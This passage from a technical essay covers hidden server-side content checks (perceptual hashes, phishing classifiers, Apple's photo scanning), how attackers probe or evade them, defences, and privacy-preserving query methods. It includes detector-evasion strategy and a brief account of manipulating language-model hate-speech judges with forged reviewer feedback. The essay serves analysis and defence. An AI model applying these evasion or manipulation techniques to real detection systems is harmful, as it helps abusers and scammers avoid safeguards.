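Bing's result is less impressive than it looks, because Bing also failed to find most of the unaltered pictures. But the results for TinEye and Google show that an attacker may need almost no feedback if the hidden system resembles one they can run themselves. Using several hashes didn't solve the problem. When Hao and colleagues built a search system that used five hashes, an attacker who knew all five altered the pictures to defeat them all at once, and no search found the original.

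Later studies disagree about how robust these hashes are. *Robustness of Practical Perceptual Hashing Algorithms to Hash-Evasion and Hash-Inversion Attacks* (Madden, Bhavsar and colleagues, 2024) found that PhotoDNA, PDQ and NeuralHash resisted attack significantly better than earlier work suggested. *ATKSCOPES* (Zhang, Sun and colleagues, 2025) then proposed a unified attack on perceptual hashing that alters images at several resolutions. The white-box attacks that evaded NeuralHash every time are a better guide to its robustness, since anyone with a phone can extract the model.

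### Chrome's visible verdicts and Apple's silence

Chrome has to warn users before they type a password, so it can't hide the server's verdict. An attacker can put a phishing page on a public website, open it in Chrome and see whether a warning appears. Chrome added a milder pop-up in 2026, and if the attacker sees that instead of the full warning, the page may be close to passing the server's check.

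Probing Chrome is still harder than probing a classifier in a laboratory. Each test reveals the page to Google, which may blocklist the whole domain if it confirms the detection. Chrome may also reuse a stored verdict if the attacker tests a new version at the same address. Moving to a new domain avoids both problems but changes the site's reputation, so the attacker can't be sure whether a different verdict was caused by the new version of the page or the new domain.

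Apple's phone would have sent an encrypted voucher with every photo and received no verdict. Apple planned to publish the match threshold and display it on the phone, but users would not have known how many of their own photos had matched. The servers would have checked accounts only periodically, so passing the threshold would not have triggered an immediate reaction.

### Signals that remain without a verdict

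Even if the device never receives a verdict, an attacker may be able to infer it from what the operator does next.

| Signal | What it reveals | How to weaken it |
|---|---|---|
| Account suspension | The server and reviewers confirmed enough items | Wait a random time before suspending |
| A site's appearance on a public blocklist | The operator judged the site dangerous | Release new entries in batches |
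| Response time | Whether the server needed a slower check | Send every reply after the same time |
| Network traffic | Whether the device sent more data or received a longer reply | Use the same number and size of messages |
| A visit from the operator's crawler | The page may have aroused suspicion | Also visit pages at random |

Suppose the server replies in 40 milliseconds when it can judge a page by the site's reputation, but takes 400 when a larger model has to read the page. An attacker can then tell which pages reached the larger model, even if no warning appears. Making every reply take 400 milliseconds would remove this signal but slow down the queries that now take 40.

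Blocklists are harder to hide because browsers need them to block sites. Adding new entries in batches would delay protection for users, and a site that lasts ten minutes may be gone before the next batch. Traffic in Apple's system would have revealed little, since phones would have sent a voucher for every photo, but Apple could not have hidden an account suspension from the account's owner.

### What one sacrificed account reveals

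Someone who wants to know whether a particular photo is on Apple's list could fill an account with 30 matching photos, add the one in question and wait. If Apple disables the account, the last photo probably matched. The test gives at most one bit of information, and the attacker loses the account if the answer is positive.

The 30 photos would have to be real abuse images, because Apple's reviewers would have left the account alone if the matches were forgeries. The attacker would therefore have to commit a serious crime, and would also be reported to a child-safety organisation if the answer was positive.

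An attacker can learn more from one account by adding 32 candidate photos one at a time and waiting after each. The account may be disabled after any of the 32 or survive them all, so there are 33 possible outcomes, which can reveal up to five bits. Debenedetti and colleagues use the same idea and compare it to finding the highest floor from which an egg can fall without breaking when you have only one egg, so you start at the bottom and go up one floor at a time. If Apple waited a random time before disabling accounts, the attacker couldn't tell which photo had caused it and would learn closer to one bit.

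The most efficient attack in Debenedetti and colleagues' comparison made 328 queries, and the model classified 244 of them as bad. If each test gave one yes-or-no answer, an attack of that size would use up 244 accounts, each containing 30 abuse images. The comparison used an image classifier, so this is only a rough guide to attacking Apple's system. But it shows that a threshold of 30 and a phone that doesn't reveal the verdict make probing far harder than in a system that reacts to every item.

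### Making each answer less useful

The simplest measure is to return a verdict without a score, since a browser doesn't need a score to decide whether to show a warning. Withholding the score slows an attacker down but doesn't stop them. Debenedetti and colleagues evaded a commercial filter for adult images using only its verdicts on whether each image was likely to be adult. The altered images were noticeably distorted but still recognisable.

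Delaying verdicts slows any attack in which each query depends on the previous answer, although each answer still reveals as much information. If verdicts took a day and an attacker had to make 328 queries in sequence, the attack would take almost a year. Some methods are less affected because they test many small changes from the same starting point, which an attacker can submit all at once. Delay is reasonable for stored photos but not for phishing warnings.

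**Query limits** force attackers to use more accounts. In the test on the commercial filter, an ordinary attack typically made 225 queries, and the filter judged 172 of them bad. A version designed to avoid bad verdicts made 311 queries, but the filter judged only 79 bad. Meta restricts accounts for a day after seven violations. Under a similar policy, the first attack would need about 25 accounts and the second about 12. The service tested imposed no such penalty.

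An operator should also limit queries that don't get a bad verdict. In *Rewriting the Budget*, Salmani, Abdollahpoorrostam and Moosavi-Dezfooli (2025) note that some stealthy attacks make about a million harmless queries for every hundred bad ones. On X, which allows 2,400 posts a day, they estimate that the bad queries would use up 10 accounts and the harmless ones about 400. Their own attack balances the two and reduces the total by up to 40% in some settings.

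These calculations assume that the attacker is an evader, who is penalized when the server confirms an item. A framer's failed forgeries are harmless pictures that the server rejects, so a limit based only on confirmed items would let the framer keep trying. The operator should count rejected flags too. If the system accepts anonymous queries to protect privacy, it can't apply an ordinary per-user limit.

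*Taking off the Rose-Tinted Glasses* (2024) argues that even a few hundred bad queries are enough to alert a defender. That is true if the defender can link the queries to each other, which is harder when they come from many accounts.

### Detecting a series of similar queries

In *Stateful Detection of Black-Box Adversarial Attacks*, Chen, Carlini and Wagner (2019) proposed storing past queries and searching them for the many near-identical items that probing usually requires. Their system tracked each account separately and banned those that submitted too many similar images. An attacker could avoid this by spreading the queries over several accounts.

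*Blacklight* instead compares each query with a shared history from all accounts and refuses to answer if it is too similar to an earlier one. This initially reduced the success of several leading attacks to zero. The history was meant to be cleared about once a day, but *Blacklight* calculated that even the fastest attack would take about three years if the attacker waited for each reset.

Attackers can also learn from the refusals themselves. In *Stateful Defenses for Machine Learning Models Are Not Yet Secure*, Feng, Fawaz and colleagues (2023) first sent queries to find out how different two images had to be to avoid a refusal. They then adapted existing attacks to change images just enough to avoid one. Against four defences, including *Blacklight*, the best adapted attacks raised the success rate from close to zero to almost 100%.

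Lee, Fang and Chang (2026) respond with two changes in *Enhancing Stateful Detection of Adversarial Attacks with Soft-labels' Temporality*. Their detector compares secret, randomly chosen parts of images, which makes it harder for attackers to learn what counts as similar. It then examines how the model's scores change over time. Scores for similar frames from a security camera vary independently, whereas an attacker chooses each query in response to earlier answers. The server can use this pattern even if it never sends the scores to users.

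In tests, the detector found all the attacks and withstood the method that Feng and colleagues had used. Its false positive rate was at most 6%, compared with 42% for an earlier defence. But a 6% rate would still be high for a service with millions of users, almost none of whom are probing it. An attacker who studies the new detector may also find a way around it, as happened with *Blacklight*.

Similar queries are also normal in a two-stage check, because thousands of people may open the same phishing page and a photo library may contain bursts of nearly identical shots. For web pages, the operator could look for a site whose content changes slightly between visits while its score moves steadily towards the threshold. The server would then have to receive enough of each page to compare versions, and it would have to keep a history of what users sent, which reduces users' privacy.

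If the operator suspects that a client is an attacker, it can silently stop sending verdicts to that client. A visible refusal would help the attacker learn the detector's rules. But if the operator is wrong, an ordinary user loses protection. In the running example, the server correctly confirms 931 of 1,000 bad items. If it withheld 6% of those verdicts from innocent users, about 56 people would miss a warning, and recall would fall from 93.1% to 87.5%. For a browser, it is safer to keep showing warnings and limit how quickly a suspicious client can test new pages.

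### Explanations and appeals

People need to know why a system has acted against them, but attackers can use a detailed explanation to work out what to change. A warning that a page imitates a bank lets the user make a sensible decision, but adding that the logo raised the score by 0.2 mainly helps the scammer. Designers can usually give the general reason and the item concerned without naming the features the model relied on.

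An appeal lets an attacker probe the system a second time, and the appeal process may itself be open to attack. *Whitewashing Hate, Smearing Harmless Content* (2026) studies language models that judge whether a text is hateful and then reconsider after feedback. The attacker writes feedback that looks like a reviewer's comment and argues for the wrong answer, either to clear a hateful text or to condemn a harmless one. If the server check is a language model, a person should review the arguments in an appeal instead of the same model.

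Probing a system through human appeals takes a lot of time and money, especially if each appeal requires an established account. Appeals help someone who has wrongly lost their photos much more than they help someone probing the system. But users can't appeal a verdict they don't know about, so a system that doesn't notify them needs more careful checks before it acts. Under Apple's design, users would have learned of the decision only when they lost their accounts.

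### Matching disclosure to the action

The device should learn the server's verdict if the action that follows can't work otherwise. For example, a warning protects someone only if they see it in time, so the device needs the verdict to show it. A report to an authority can be sent without the device learning the verdict.

| Action | What the user should learn | When |
|---|---|---|
| Warning about a page | The verdict and a general reason, without a score | Immediately |
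| Blocking an upload or message | That it was blocked, and how to appeal | When it is blocked |
| Sending an item to human review | Nothing yet | After review, if the operator acts |
| Suspending an account | The rule concerned, and how to appeal | When the suspension starts, after human review |
| Reporting someone to an authority | Nothing through the device | Later, if the law allows or requires it |

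A service that warns users and also reports them should not use the same hidden model and threshold for both. Otherwise, an attacker can use the warnings to learn which items would lead to a report.

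## Querying the server without exposing the user's data

How much a server has to learn about an item depends mainly on whether it looks the item up in a list or runs a model on it. A lookup only has to check whether two short codes are equal, and there are efficient ways to do that without revealing the code. A model needs the item itself, or at least data computed from it. The device can send that data in a form the server can read, as Chrome does with the text of a suspected scam page. Otherwise the server has to compute on encrypted data or run the model in hardware that prevents the operator's own staff from seeing the data.

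The method must also reveal the result to the right party, which was the server in Apple's threshold PSI and is the browser in Safe Browsing.

### What hash prefixes reveal

A four-byte hash prefix hides an address only among the others that share it. If a server lists 100 billion pages, about 23 share each prefix, but the user is not equally likely to have visited each of them. Educated Guesswork notes that users are far more likely to visit facebook.com than an obscure domain whose hash has the same prefix.

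Several prefixes from one address narrow the choice much further. Under real-time checks, Chrome may send the prefixes for a page and for its site in the same request. Every page on the site shares the site's prefix, but on a site with 1,000 pages, there is only about a 1 in 4 million chance that another page shares the page's own prefix. The server can therefore identify almost any page it already knows about, but not a private link that contains a long random code, because it has nothing to compare the prefixes with.

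Meta's *How Advanced Browsing Protection Works in Messenger* (2026) states that if one lookup reveals *B* bits, looking up *P* parts of an address reveals *P* × *B* bits. Looking up eight four-byte prefixes therefore reveals 256 bits.

If the server can link a user's queries, it may also learn who the user is. In an example from Educated Guesswork, someone opens the editing page of one account and then another person's Instagram profile. The first visit suggests who the user is, and the second shows whose profile they are looking at.

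Checking a local list first doesn't protect users from a dishonest server. The server could put the prefix of facebook.com on that list and never confirm the hits. Users would see no warning, but their browsers would contact the server when they visited Facebook.

### Hiding who sent the query

Oblivious HTTP (OHTTP) puts a relay between the user and the server. Chrome uses one run by Fastly, a company that delivers web content for other firms. Google describes the process:

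1. Chrome encrypts the hash prefixes with a public key that belongs to Safe Browsing.
2. It sends them to Fastly's relay, which sees the user's IP address but can't decrypt the prefixes.
3. The relay removes the IP address and other possible identifiers, then forwards the encrypted prefixes to Google.
4. Google decrypts the prefixes and looks them up. The answer returns through the relay.

Google learns which prefixes someone looked up, and Fastly learns who looked something up. Google can often work out the page from the prefixes, so Li and Bawa overstated the protection when they wrote that no one, including Google, knows what website the user is visiting. The relay hides who visited the page, but only while the two companies keep their records apart.

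OHTTP also encrypts each request separately and mixes requests from many users on one connection. If a browser instead kept its own connection open through the relay, Google could link all the requests on it without seeing an IP address. Even with OHTTP, Google may be able to infer that requests arriving in quick succession came from the same browser.

Apple's Live Caller ID Lookup, which identifies callers and known spam numbers, sends queries through two relays run by different parties. According to Apple's *Understanding how Live Caller ID Lookup preserves privacy*, the first relay removes the IP address and can't see where the request is going.

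A relay that hides the user's IP address adds a network hop but barely changes the server's work, so it is one of the lowest-overhead protections. It can carry queries to a model as easily as queries to a list. But a private photo or chat message often identifies its owner, so hiding the IP address gives users little privacy when a service sends whole items.

### Looking up leaked passwords with blinded hashes

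A service that warns people about leaked passwords can't safely publish ordinary hashes of them, because anyone could hash likely guesses and see which ones are on the list. Asking users to send a hash prefix is also risky, because some passwords are so common that the prefix can reveal which one a user probably has.

PSI can protect both sides. Google's *Private Set Membership* describes a protocol for checking a single item. Google hashes its set with one secret key, and the device blinds its query with another. The steps below show how this kind of blinding works. They use the same toy arithmetic as the example of Apple's protocol, where every result is a remainder after division by 101.

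1. As in that example, the server blinds the value 20, which here stands for a leaked password, with its secret number 7 and stores the result, 39. It does the same for the rest of the list and sorts the results into buckets.
2. The device wants to check the same password, so it also starts from 20. It picks a random number, 3, and sends 3 × 20 = 60.
3. The server multiplies 60 by 7. The result is 420, which leaves 16, and the server returns that.
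4. The device removes its random number by dividing by 3. In this arithmetic, that means multiplying by 34, because 3 × 34 leaves 1. The result is 544, which leaves 39.
5. The device looks for 39 in the relevant bucket and finds it.

The server can't determine which password produced 60 because it doesn't have the random number. The device receives the verdict, but it can't test other passwords against the bucket unless the server processes each guess. An operator could protect a list of scam sites the same way, so that scammers could no longer test their addresses offline.

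The query usually still reveals to the server which bucket the device needs. Educated Guesswork describes a password checker by Li, Pal and others that reduces this leak with "frequency-smoothed" buckets. The checker spreads common passwords over many buckets, so the bucket a device needs is not strong evidence of any one common password.

### Retrieving an entry without revealing which one

Private information retrieval (PIR) can hide even which bucket the device requests. The simplest way to hide a query is to download the whole list and search it on the device. Meta rejected this for Messenger because its list of dangerous links is too large, changes too often and would help attackers who obtained all of it.

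Educated Guesswork's *ELI15* explains a cheaper method that arranges the list in a square. Suppose the server has nine records, each a single digit:

| | Column 1 | Column 2 | Column 3 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Row 1 | 2 | 7 | 4 |
| Row 2 | 5 | 1 | 8 |
| Row 3 | 3 | 6 | 9 |

The device wants the 8 in row 2. It could send the numbers 0, 0 and 1, and have the server multiply each column by its number and add up each row. This would return 4, 8 and 9, but the server would see that the device wanted column 3. The device therefore encrypts the three numbers with homomorphic encryption, which lets the server calculate with numbers it can't read. A toy version works like this:

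1. The device chooses a secret key, 1,009. To encrypt a digit, it adds a random multiple of 10 and a random multiple of the key. The first 0 becomes 0 + 30 + 5 × 1,009 = 5,075. The second becomes 0 + 10 + 8 × 1,009 = 8,082. The 1 becomes 1 + 20 + 6 × 1,009 = 6,075.
2. The server receives 5,075, 8,082 and 6,075. For row 2, it calculates 5 × 5,075 + 1 × 8,082 + 8 × 6,075 = 82,057. It does the same for the other rows and gets 91,024 and 118,392.
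3. The device divides 82,057 by 1,009, which leaves 328. The last digit is 8, the record it wanted.

Numbers this small would be easy to break, so practical systems use larger ones and also hide values under random noise that the key removes. To look up an address, they first hash it to find its place in the table.

For a million records, the device sends 1,000 encrypted numbers and receives 1,000, instead of downloading the whole list. The server still has to process every record, because skipping one would reveal that the device hadn't requested it. The device in the example could also decrypt the other two answers and read the 4 and the 9, so basic PIR protects the user's query but doesn't necessarily keep the list secret.

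Kogan and Corrigan-Gibbs's Checklist (2021) avoids processing the whole list by using two servers. In simplified form, the device first requests the sum of a random set of entries, such as 2, 5 and 9, from one server and gets 14. To look up entry 5 later, it requests the sum of entries 2 and 9 from the other server, gets 8, and subtracts to find that entry 5 is 6. The second server reads only two entries, and the request doesn't include the number 5. The real protocol adds some randomness, because the second request would otherwise reveal that the device isn't looking up entry 2 or 9.

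Checklist describes building its system into Firefox for Safe Browsing lookups. According to figures quoted by Educated Guesswork, the system used 3.3 times as much communication and 9.8 times as much server computation as the existing one. It also depends on the two servers not sharing the data they receive.

### What PIR costs

*FrodoPIR* (Davidson, Pestana and Celi) puts the cost of single-server private information retrieval (PIR) at about $1 for 100,000 queries on a million one-kilobyte records, and each response takes less than a second. In 2024 Safe Browsing assessed more than 10 billion web addresses and files a day. If each needed one such query, the cost would be about $100,000 a day. If a local list of 3 million prefixes first cleared all but 1 in 180, the daily cost would fall to about $560. These figures are rough because a real list would have a different size and an address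 may need several lookups.

Newer PIR systems are faster. *ZipPIR* (2026) needs only 400 bytes of communication to set up and is at least 20% faster than YPIR, the fastest alternative in its comparison of systems that need no storage on the device. *VIPIR* (2026) runs on graphics processors and reports server computation 12.5 to 77.9 times faster than YPIR on ordinary processors. When it handles queries in batches on two graphics processors, *GPIR* (2026) reaches up to 297 times the throughput of an earlier open-source system for graphics processors.

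The speed-ups don't translate directly into savings, because graphics processors cost more and the server has to wait for a batch to fill before running it. Tests may also leave out delays that users would notice. *High-Throughput Private Information Retrieval with on-CPU Accelerators* (2026), for instance, measures throughput on requests that have already arrived at the server.

### A two-stage web filter with PIR

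Since 2025, Apple has let developers build web filters, such as those for parents or schools, that combine a local list with PIR. *Filter and tunnel network traffic with NetworkExtension* (Dos Santos, 2025) explains that the device holds a Bloom filter, a compressed list that can produce false matches but never misses an entry.

Suppose the filter has ten bits, all 0 at first. One blocked address sets bits 2 and 7 to 1, and another sets bits 4 and 9. An address that maps to bits 3 and 7 can't be on the list, because bit 3 is still 0. An address that maps to bits 2 and 9 looks listed even though it isn't, because both bits are 1. The device sends an encrypted PIR query through Apple's relay to the developer's server only when an address looks listed. It then decrypts the answer and blocks the address if it is on the list.

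This limits the number of resource-intensive queries, but as with the old Safe Browsing, new sites go undetected until the local list updates. Eric Lawrence, who works on Microsoft Defender, wrote in text/plain's *First Look* (2025) that Apple allowed updates at most once every 45 minutes.

Lawrence lists other things an operator loses when it can't see the queries. It can't discover new threats from the addresses people visit, or rescan addresses that suddenly become popular. It can't use the redirects that led to a page as evidence, and a company's security team can't find out which computer tried to open a malicious link. The server also can't return a graded verdict, such as a warning the user may override. Lawrence still calls the design brilliant for many uses, including parental controls. Under these limits, Chrome's server check would lose much of its advantage over the local models,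 because it relies on evidence about the site as well as the page.

### Meta's link check in encrypted chats

Messenger's standard protection uses models on the phone to find malicious links in encrypted chats. An optional setting, Advanced Browsing Protection, also checks each link the user opens against a server list of millions of suspicious sites. Meta found that searching the whole list with private information retrieval (PIR) was not yet practical at its scale, so it divided the list into buckets and combined several weaker protections.

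Meta's server sends phones a set of rules for splitting domains with many malicious links into smaller buckets. For `example.com/a/b/index.html`, a rule might tell the phone to hash `example.com/a/b` instead of just `example.com`. If the phone used only the domain, all the malicious links from a popular link-shortening service would land in one huge bucket. That would slow down every query, because the server pads every reply to the size of the largest bucket. If the phone instead sent a separate bucket number for each part of a link, the numbers together could identify the link.

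When someone taps a link, the check proceeds as follows:

1. The phone applies the rules and takes the first two bytes of the resulting hash as the bucket number. This gives 65,536 possible buckets.
2. It encrypts the bucket number for a protected virtual machine on Meta's servers. It also prepares a blinded hash for each part of the link, plus dummies so that the number of hashes doesn't reveal the link's length.
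3. It sends everything through a relay run by another company, which removes the IP address.
4. The server applies its secret key to the blinded hashes. The protected machine fetches the bucket, and the phone receives both.
5. The phone removes the blinding and compares the results with the bucket. If it finds a match, it warns the user.

The protected machine encrypts its memory, but someone who controls the server could still see which parts it reads. The machine could hide this by reading every bucket for every query. Meta reduces that work with Path ORAM, an algorithm that hides which data a program is retrieving without reading all of it.

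Someone who broke into the protected machine would see only a bucket number and no IP address. With 5 million entries on the list, a bucket would hold about 76 on average, and many harmless links would lead to the same bucket. A bucket number therefore reveals much less than several four-byte prefixes do.

### Matching images privately

Perceptual hashes are harder to look up privately, because a useful system may have to match hashes that are similar but not identical. Kulshrestha and Mayer (2021), in *Identifying Harmful Media in End-to-End Encrypted Communication*, designed protocols for this problem. Some do the matching on the phone, which is acceptable only if the hashes can be public. Others involve the server and can keep the hash list secret, without notifying the user of a match.

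The IETF's *Techniques for detecting known illegal material in end-to-end encrypted communications* compares what the server learns in two versions of the check. The exact version reveals whether the image's hash is on the list, and the approximate version reveals whether it is within a set distance of a listed hash. Neither version has a threshold like Apple's, so a single false match exposes a user. At the one-in-a-million error rate that Apple assumed, a service with 4.5 billion images a day would produce 4,500 false matches daily.

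Kulshrestha and Mayer considered their protocols practical for phones and the additional risk of missed images limited. But the approximate version takes about 27 seconds to check one image against a million others and misses almost 17% of slightly altered copies. Someone sending a photo would notice the delay if the app waited for the result.

In *Outside Looking In*, Kamara, Knodel and colleagues (2021) object to such systems however well the cryptography works. Under their definition of end-to-end encryption, a company that carries a message can't learn anything about its content. A protocol that reveals to the company only whether a photo matched still doesn't meet that definition. They favour user reports and analysis of metadata, such as how many messages each user sends. The objection is weaker against Meta's link check because only the phone receives the result, although the bucket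 number still reveals a little about the link.

### Running a model on encrypted data

A device can send a model a summary of an item instead of the item itself, but the summary may not be private. Asi, Boemer and colleagues (2024), in *Wally*, warn that a server may be able to reverse an image embedding and infer sensitive details of the photo. Apple therefore encrypts the embeddings in Enhanced Visual Search, which labels landmarks in people's photos. It isn't a harmful-content detector, but it divides the work in a similar way, as Apple explains:

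1. A model on the phone looks for a part of the photo that may show a landmark.
2. The phone turns that part into an embedding, rounds the numbers to save space and encrypts them.
3. It compares the embedding with a stored list of cluster centres and chooses the closest cluster. The phone sends the cluster number and the encrypted embedding through a relay.
4. The server compares the encrypted embedding with each landmark in the cluster and returns encrypted similarity scores.
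5. The phone decrypts the scores, and another small model chooses the best match.

The comparison uses the same arithmetic as PIR. If the photo's embedding is (3, 1) and a landmark's is (2, 4), the score is 3 × 2 + 1 × 4 = 10. The server only has to multiply encrypted numbers by numbers it knows and add the results. A full neural network also needs steps such as replacing negative numbers with zero, which take much more computation under encryption.

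The server can see the cluster number, which might show that a photo contains, say, a castle. Phones therefore send fake queries for random clusters, on average one or two for each real query, and spread them over time. Each phone has to send fewer fakes as more people use the system. At Apple's setting of ε = 0.8, any pattern the server sees is at most about 2.2 times as likely with a given user's photo library as without it, except for a small failure probability, δ. Apple's article gives δ as one in a million, while *Apple's Deployment of Homomorphic Encryption at Scale* (Rishi and Mughees, 2025) gives one in a billion.

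Rishi and Mughees report that Apple's system handles more than 25,000 queries per second on a test collection of 3.2 million entries, assuming 10,000 processor cores. Each query needs 0.56 MB of communication. Tiptoe, an earlier system that processes the whole collection for every query, handles 909 queries per second at 17.4 MB each. Apple's system therefore uses about 0.4 seconds of one core's time per query, compared with 11 seconds for Tiptoe. Its throughput is more than 27 times Tiptoe's, near the top of the range of 7 to 29 times that *Wally* reports across different settings.

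The method suits photo labels, which can wait while the phone spreads out its queries, but not phishing warnings, which are needed right away. Using it for phishing detection would also let scammers get the scores for their own pages without the server seeing what they were testing.

### Running a model in protected hardware

Attested hardware lets a server run an ordinary model on readable content without letting the operator see it. The processor encrypts the memory of a virtual machine and signs a report on the software that the machine started with. In Meta's link check, the report also contains a public key whose private half never leaves the machine. The phone checks the signatures before it encrypts anything with that key.

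Meta uses the same approach in WhatsApp's Private Processing, which can summarise private messages with AI without giving Meta or WhatsApp access to them. A content detector could run a large classifier this way and return only the verdict. This is currently the most practical way to run a large model on a private item without showing the item to the operator.

The user has to trust the chip's maker and the software inside the machine. A signed report proves which program is running, but someone still has to check what that program does. When Meta described its link check in March 2026, it planned to release the material outside researchers would need for this, but had not yet done so. A secret model is harder to check because the report can show that everyone gets the same model, but not what content it detects.

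### Limiting clients that the server can't recognise

Hiding users better makes it harder to stop someone from probing the system. With OHTTP alone, the server can't count one person's queries, but it can still read them, so a detector such as *Blacklight*, which looks for similar queries across all accounts, could work. With PIR or encrypted embeddings, the server can't compare the queries either. Its verdicts are hidden from it too, so it can't limit clients whose flags it keeps rejecting.

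Anonymous tokens are a partial answer. Apple's web filters and caller lookup use a protocol called Privacy Pass, in which a device first proves that it is entitled to use the service and then receives a supply of tokens. It spends them on queries that the server can't trace back to it. This relies on a blind signature, which the following toy example shows with remainders after division by 55:

1. The device picks a random token, 8, and a blinding number, 2. It multiplies 8 by 2³ to get 64, which leaves 9, and sends 9 to the issuer.
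2. The issuer signs 9 by raising it to a secret power, 27. This leaves 4, which it returns.
3. The device divides 4 by its blinding number. The result, 2, is the signature for token 8.
4. The device later sends 8 and 2 with a query. The server checks that 2³ = 8 and records the token so that nobody can use it again.

The issuer saw only 9 and 4, so it can't recognise 8 and 2 later, even if it also runs the server. Truecaller, a caller-identification service, says it needs such tokens because any device can technically use Apple's relay.

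How much rate-limiting tokens help depends on the attack. Suppose each device gets 200 tokens a day, enough for a browser that queries the server about most new sites. Trying all possible four-byte prefixes takes about 143 million requests, or nearly 2,000 years with one device. But the most efficient yes-or-no attacks on image classifiers need only about 330 queries, which would take two days.

A two-stage check can set a tighter limit on queries because the device queries the server only about flagged items. In the running example, the local model flags about 1% of items, so someone who opens 50 pages a day needs a token roughly every other day. With a limit of five tokens a day, an attack with 330 queries would take 66 days. An attacker with 66 devices could still finish in one day, and the server couldn't tell that the queries were part of the same attack.

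Educated Guesswork adds that checking a token can take more computation than answering a simple lookup, in which case the server might as well answer everyone. That is a good argument against requiring tokens for hash-prefix lookups, but a PIR query takes enough computation to justify the check. The relay can also help by limiting traffic from individual IP addresses, since it sees them and the server doesn't.

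### Comparing the methods

Many systems combine several of these methods, so the table gives what each one reveals by itself.

| Method | What the server learns | What the device learns | Cost | Suitable for |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Hash prefixes | The prefixes, and often the page | The verdict and all full hashes with those prefixes | A few bytes and a simple lookup | Exact lists that needn't be secret |
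| Oblivious HTTP | The query, but not the IP address | The server's reply | One extra network hop | Lists, and models if the content doesn't identify the user |
| Blinded hashes (PSI) | The bucket | The verdict, and entries it can't read | One bucket and a short calculation per string | Exact lists, including secret ones |
| PIR with one server | Nothing about the query | The entry, and possibly others | Work on the whole list, at about $1 per 100,000 queries in one estimate | Exact lists |
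| PIR with two servers | Nothing, unless the servers collude | The entry | For Checklist, 3.3 times the communication and 9.8 times the server computation of Safe Browsing | Exact lists |
| Private image matching | Whether the image matched | Nothing, if the operator chooses | About 27 seconds per image for a million listed images | Lists of perceptual hashes |
| Homomorphic encryption with clusters | A cluster number, hidden among fake queries | The similarity scores | 0.56 MB and about 0.4 core-seconds per query | Models that compare embeddings, if the answer can wait |
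| Attested hardware | Only what the approved software releases | The verdict, if the software returns it | Special servers, and extra work to hide memory access | Lists and large models |

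## Judging how much security rests on keeping the server model secret

Private queries protect the user from the operator, but protection against forged flags depends on keeping the server's model secret from attackers. Cryptographers distrust designs that rely on this kind of secret. *Kerckhoffs' Principle* (Petitcolas, 2023) gives the rule that "the security of a cryptosystem must lie in the choice of its keys only". Designers should assume, as the mathematician Claude Shannon put it, that "the enemy knows the system", including the algorithm and everything else except the keys.

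A hidden server check seems to break this rule. The second hash or classifier is part of the design, and secret designs tend to leak through reverse engineering, theft or a careless employee. If the check stops working once its design leaks, critics can fairly call it security through obscurity.

The usual reply is that the weights serve as the key, since an operator can publish the model's architecture and training method, keep only the weights secret, and train new ones if they leak. The number of copies also matters. Kerckhoffs objected to the French army's codebooks partly because so many people held them that any battle could expose one, whereas a server model can stay on a few well-guarded machines. Thomas, Meiklejohn and colleagues (2023), in *Robust, privacy-preserving, transparent, and auditable on-device blocklisting*, point out that Signal, an otherwise open-source messaging app,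 keeps its spam filter closed so that spammers can't read the code and adapt.

Keeping the server model secret can help. When Google replaced Gmail's published file-type model with a secret one, the success rate of the best attacks fell from 90% to 20%, although some of that drop may have come from the new model itself rather than its secrecy. A 20% success rate is still far higher than any attacker could achieve by guessing a cryptographic key.

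### Comparing the weights with a key

Software picks a 128-bit key at random from 2¹²⁸ possibilities, so knowing how the system works gives no hint of the key, and a guess with one wrong digit is useless. The server model's weights come from training, and models trained for the same job often respond to the same features, so an attacker can develop an attack on a similar model without knowing the exact weights. In the few tests of whether attacks made for one hash also work on another, success rates ranged from zero to over 60%.

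A designer might try to fix this by putting a real random key inside the model. NeuralHash turns a photo into 128 numbers, then uses a fixed table to turn those into 96 bits. The server could use the same network with a secret, randomly generated table, which the operator could replace in a moment. But the chance that a forged picture matches its target would still depend on how close their 128 numbers are. If the angle between the two sets of numbers is θ degrees, all 96 bits agree with probability (1 − θ/180)⁹⁶.

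| Angle between the forgery and its target | Chance of matching under a secret table |
|---|---|
| 45° | About 1 in a trillion |
| 10° | 0.4% |
| 1° | 59% |
| 0.1° | 95% |

An attacker who has the network can reduce the angle offline without knowing anything about the table. Jain, Creţu and colleagues did this in *Deep perceptual hashing algorithms with hidden dual purpose* (2023), using a similar network that produces 256 numbers. They altered photos of dogs until the numbers equalled those of a chosen target, and the photos still scored a median of 0.98 on a similarity scale where 1 means identical. The secret therefore has to include the features the network has learned, which aren't random.

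Madden and colleagues propose adding more randomness to the bits of perceptual hashes, because they found that random variation partly explains why these hashes resisted black-box attacks. That may slow an attacker who can only observe outputs. Judging by the calculation above, it would do much less against one who has the network.

An operator can replace a key in seconds, but to replace a server model it must train a new one, choose a threshold and measure the error rates again on flagged items. If the model is a perceptual hash, whoever holds the original images must also recompute every hash on the list. The new model may share weaknesses with the old one, especially if the operator trains it on the same data, so some of the old forgeries may still work.

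Good encryption also reveals nothing useful about the key, however many messages an attacker collects, but each visible verdict can reveal up to one bit about the server model. The model therefore gradually becomes less secret, and this happens faster in a browser that shows warnings than in a photo service that doesn't show its verdicts.

The last difference is that anyone can calculate how much work it takes to guess a key. Finding a 128-bit key takes 2¹²⁷ tries on average, or about 5 billion billion years at a trillion tries per second. For a hidden model, an operator can only report how often known attacks succeeded, and a better attack could suddenly raise that rate. Hiding the weights can make an attack harder, but the operator can't promise that it is infeasible.

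### How PhotoDNA and NeuralHash became known

Microsoft developed PhotoDNA with the computer scientist Hany Farid in 2009 and has never published the algorithm. According to Boston University's *The Broken Promise of Apple's Announced Forbidden-photo Reporting System*, storage companies receive the algorithm under licence and non-disclosure agreements, and the list of hashes in confidence.

PhotoDNA's algorithm got out despite the secrecy. Anish Athalye wrote in *Inverting PhotoDNA* (2021) that people had reverse-engineered it from public documents and that someone had leaked a compiled library, which could compute hashes but didn't reveal the mathematics. In 2026 Deryck and colleagues gave the first mathematical description of their function, which reproduces PhotoDNA's outputs, and used it to identify several design weaknesses. The news site CyberInsider reports that the researchers can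 bypass PhotoDNA, produce false matches and partly reconstruct images from their hashes.

PhotoDNA therefore stayed secret from the public for about 12 years, or about 17 counting until someone published the mathematics. Nobody knows whether attackers had it earlier. More than 150 organisations use PhotoDNA, according to a European Commission report that Leblanc-Albarel and Preneel quote, so it could have leaked from many places. Replacing it would also require all these organisations to change their systems.

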